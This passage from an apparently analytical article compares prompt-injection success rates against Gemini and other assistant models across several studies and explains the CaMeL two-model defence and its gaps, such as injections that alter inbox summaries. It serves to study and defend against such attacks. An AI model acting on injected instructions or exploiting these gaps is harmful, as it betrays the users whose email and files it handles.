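The 8.5 percent is consistent with the 94.6 percent that DeepMind measured for hardened Gemini 2.5 because the two figures measure different things. The contest counted every attempt, including those by beginners and those people made while still working out an idea. DeepMind counted how often the single best injection worked. The lower figure might be relevant to a company worried about careless mass attacks, but the higher one matters more to someone who expects a skilled attacker. The contestants could also read the conversation before writing the injection, which real attackers can rarely do.

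Gemini 2.5 Pro is now an old model. The most recent independent figures for current models come from *FrontierBreach*, an undated benchmark by the security company PromptArmor. It places injections based on real attacks into long office tasks, such as analyzing a bond portfolio.

| Model | Attack success rate | Margin of error |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Carbon | 2.4% | ±2.2 points |
| Gemini 4 Argon | 4.3% | ±2.9 points |
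| GPT-6 Astra | 7.6% | ±3.8 points |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 10.0% | ±4.2 points |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 22.4% | ±5.9 points |

*Selected results from PromptArmor, with 95 percent confidence intervals.*

The two Gemini 4 models had the lowest rates of the 22 that PromptArmor lists, but the margins of error are too wide to rank the two. The first 21 models it tested averaged 34.9 percent. Google came last in the contest, so this is a big improvement, although the two tests aren't comparable.

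Attackers do much better when they can keep trying. With hundreds of attempts at each task, the AI agents that Kurakin and colleagues used as attackers succeeded on about a third of tasks against Gemini 4 Argon and nearly all against Gemini 3.6 Flash. Both studies found the Flash model far more vulnerable, so a user's protection may depend heavily on which model handles the request. A fast, cheap model would be a natural choice for summarizing millions of emails.

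None of these tests included the layers that Google adds in Workspace. They measure how many injections the model fails to resist, leaving the other defenses to stop them, and that number is still high when the attacker is determined.

### CaMeL and the cost of separation

A rival approach is to assume that a model may follow injected instructions and to limit what can happen when it does. The best-known design is CaMeL, introduced in 2025 by Debenedetti and colleagues, including researchers from Google DeepMind.

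CaMeL divides the work between two models, as *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) explains. A privileged model reads only the user's request and writes a plan as a short Python program. A quarantined model reads the emails and files, but it can't call tools or change the plan. If a user asks Gemini to find the landlord's address in an email and send the lease there, the plan might have three steps: fetch the email, have the quarantined model extract the address, and send the lease. An injection in the email can't add a fourth step that opens a window, because the privileged model never reads the email.

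The injection could still make the quarantined model return the wrong address. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), CaMeL deals with this by having the software that runs the plan label each value with where it came from and who may read it. Before sending the lease, the software checks the labels against a security policy. It could then refuse to send a private file to an address that came from a stranger's email, however plausible the address looked.

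*Can CaMeLs Talk?* extends the idea to systems in which an orchestrator directs several agents, as in Gemini. It treats anything an agent returns after reading outside text as untrusted data, so that output can't influence the plan the way event titles did in the calendar attacks.

According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), CaMeL stops nearly all the injections in AgentDojo and completes a comparable share of ordinary tasks. CaMeL doesn't depend on recognizing malicious wording, so attackers gain much less by rewording their injections.

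But the design makes an assistant less useful. CaMeL has to plan before any emails are read, so it has the usual trouble with open-ended requests, where the right steps depend on what the emails say. Someone also has to write the security policies, and strict ones will block legitimate requests or add to approval fatigue. Running two models and tracking every value also takes more computing. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* predicts that the loss of usefulness will shrink as models get better at planning and writing code. That should help with complicated plans, but a model still can't base its plan on an email it isn't allowed to read.

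CaMeL also does little about false summaries. For an inbox summary, the plan is to fetch the emails, have the quarantined model summarize them, and show the result to the user. An injection can change the summary without changing any of those steps, and the labels don't help, because the user is allowed to read all of it.
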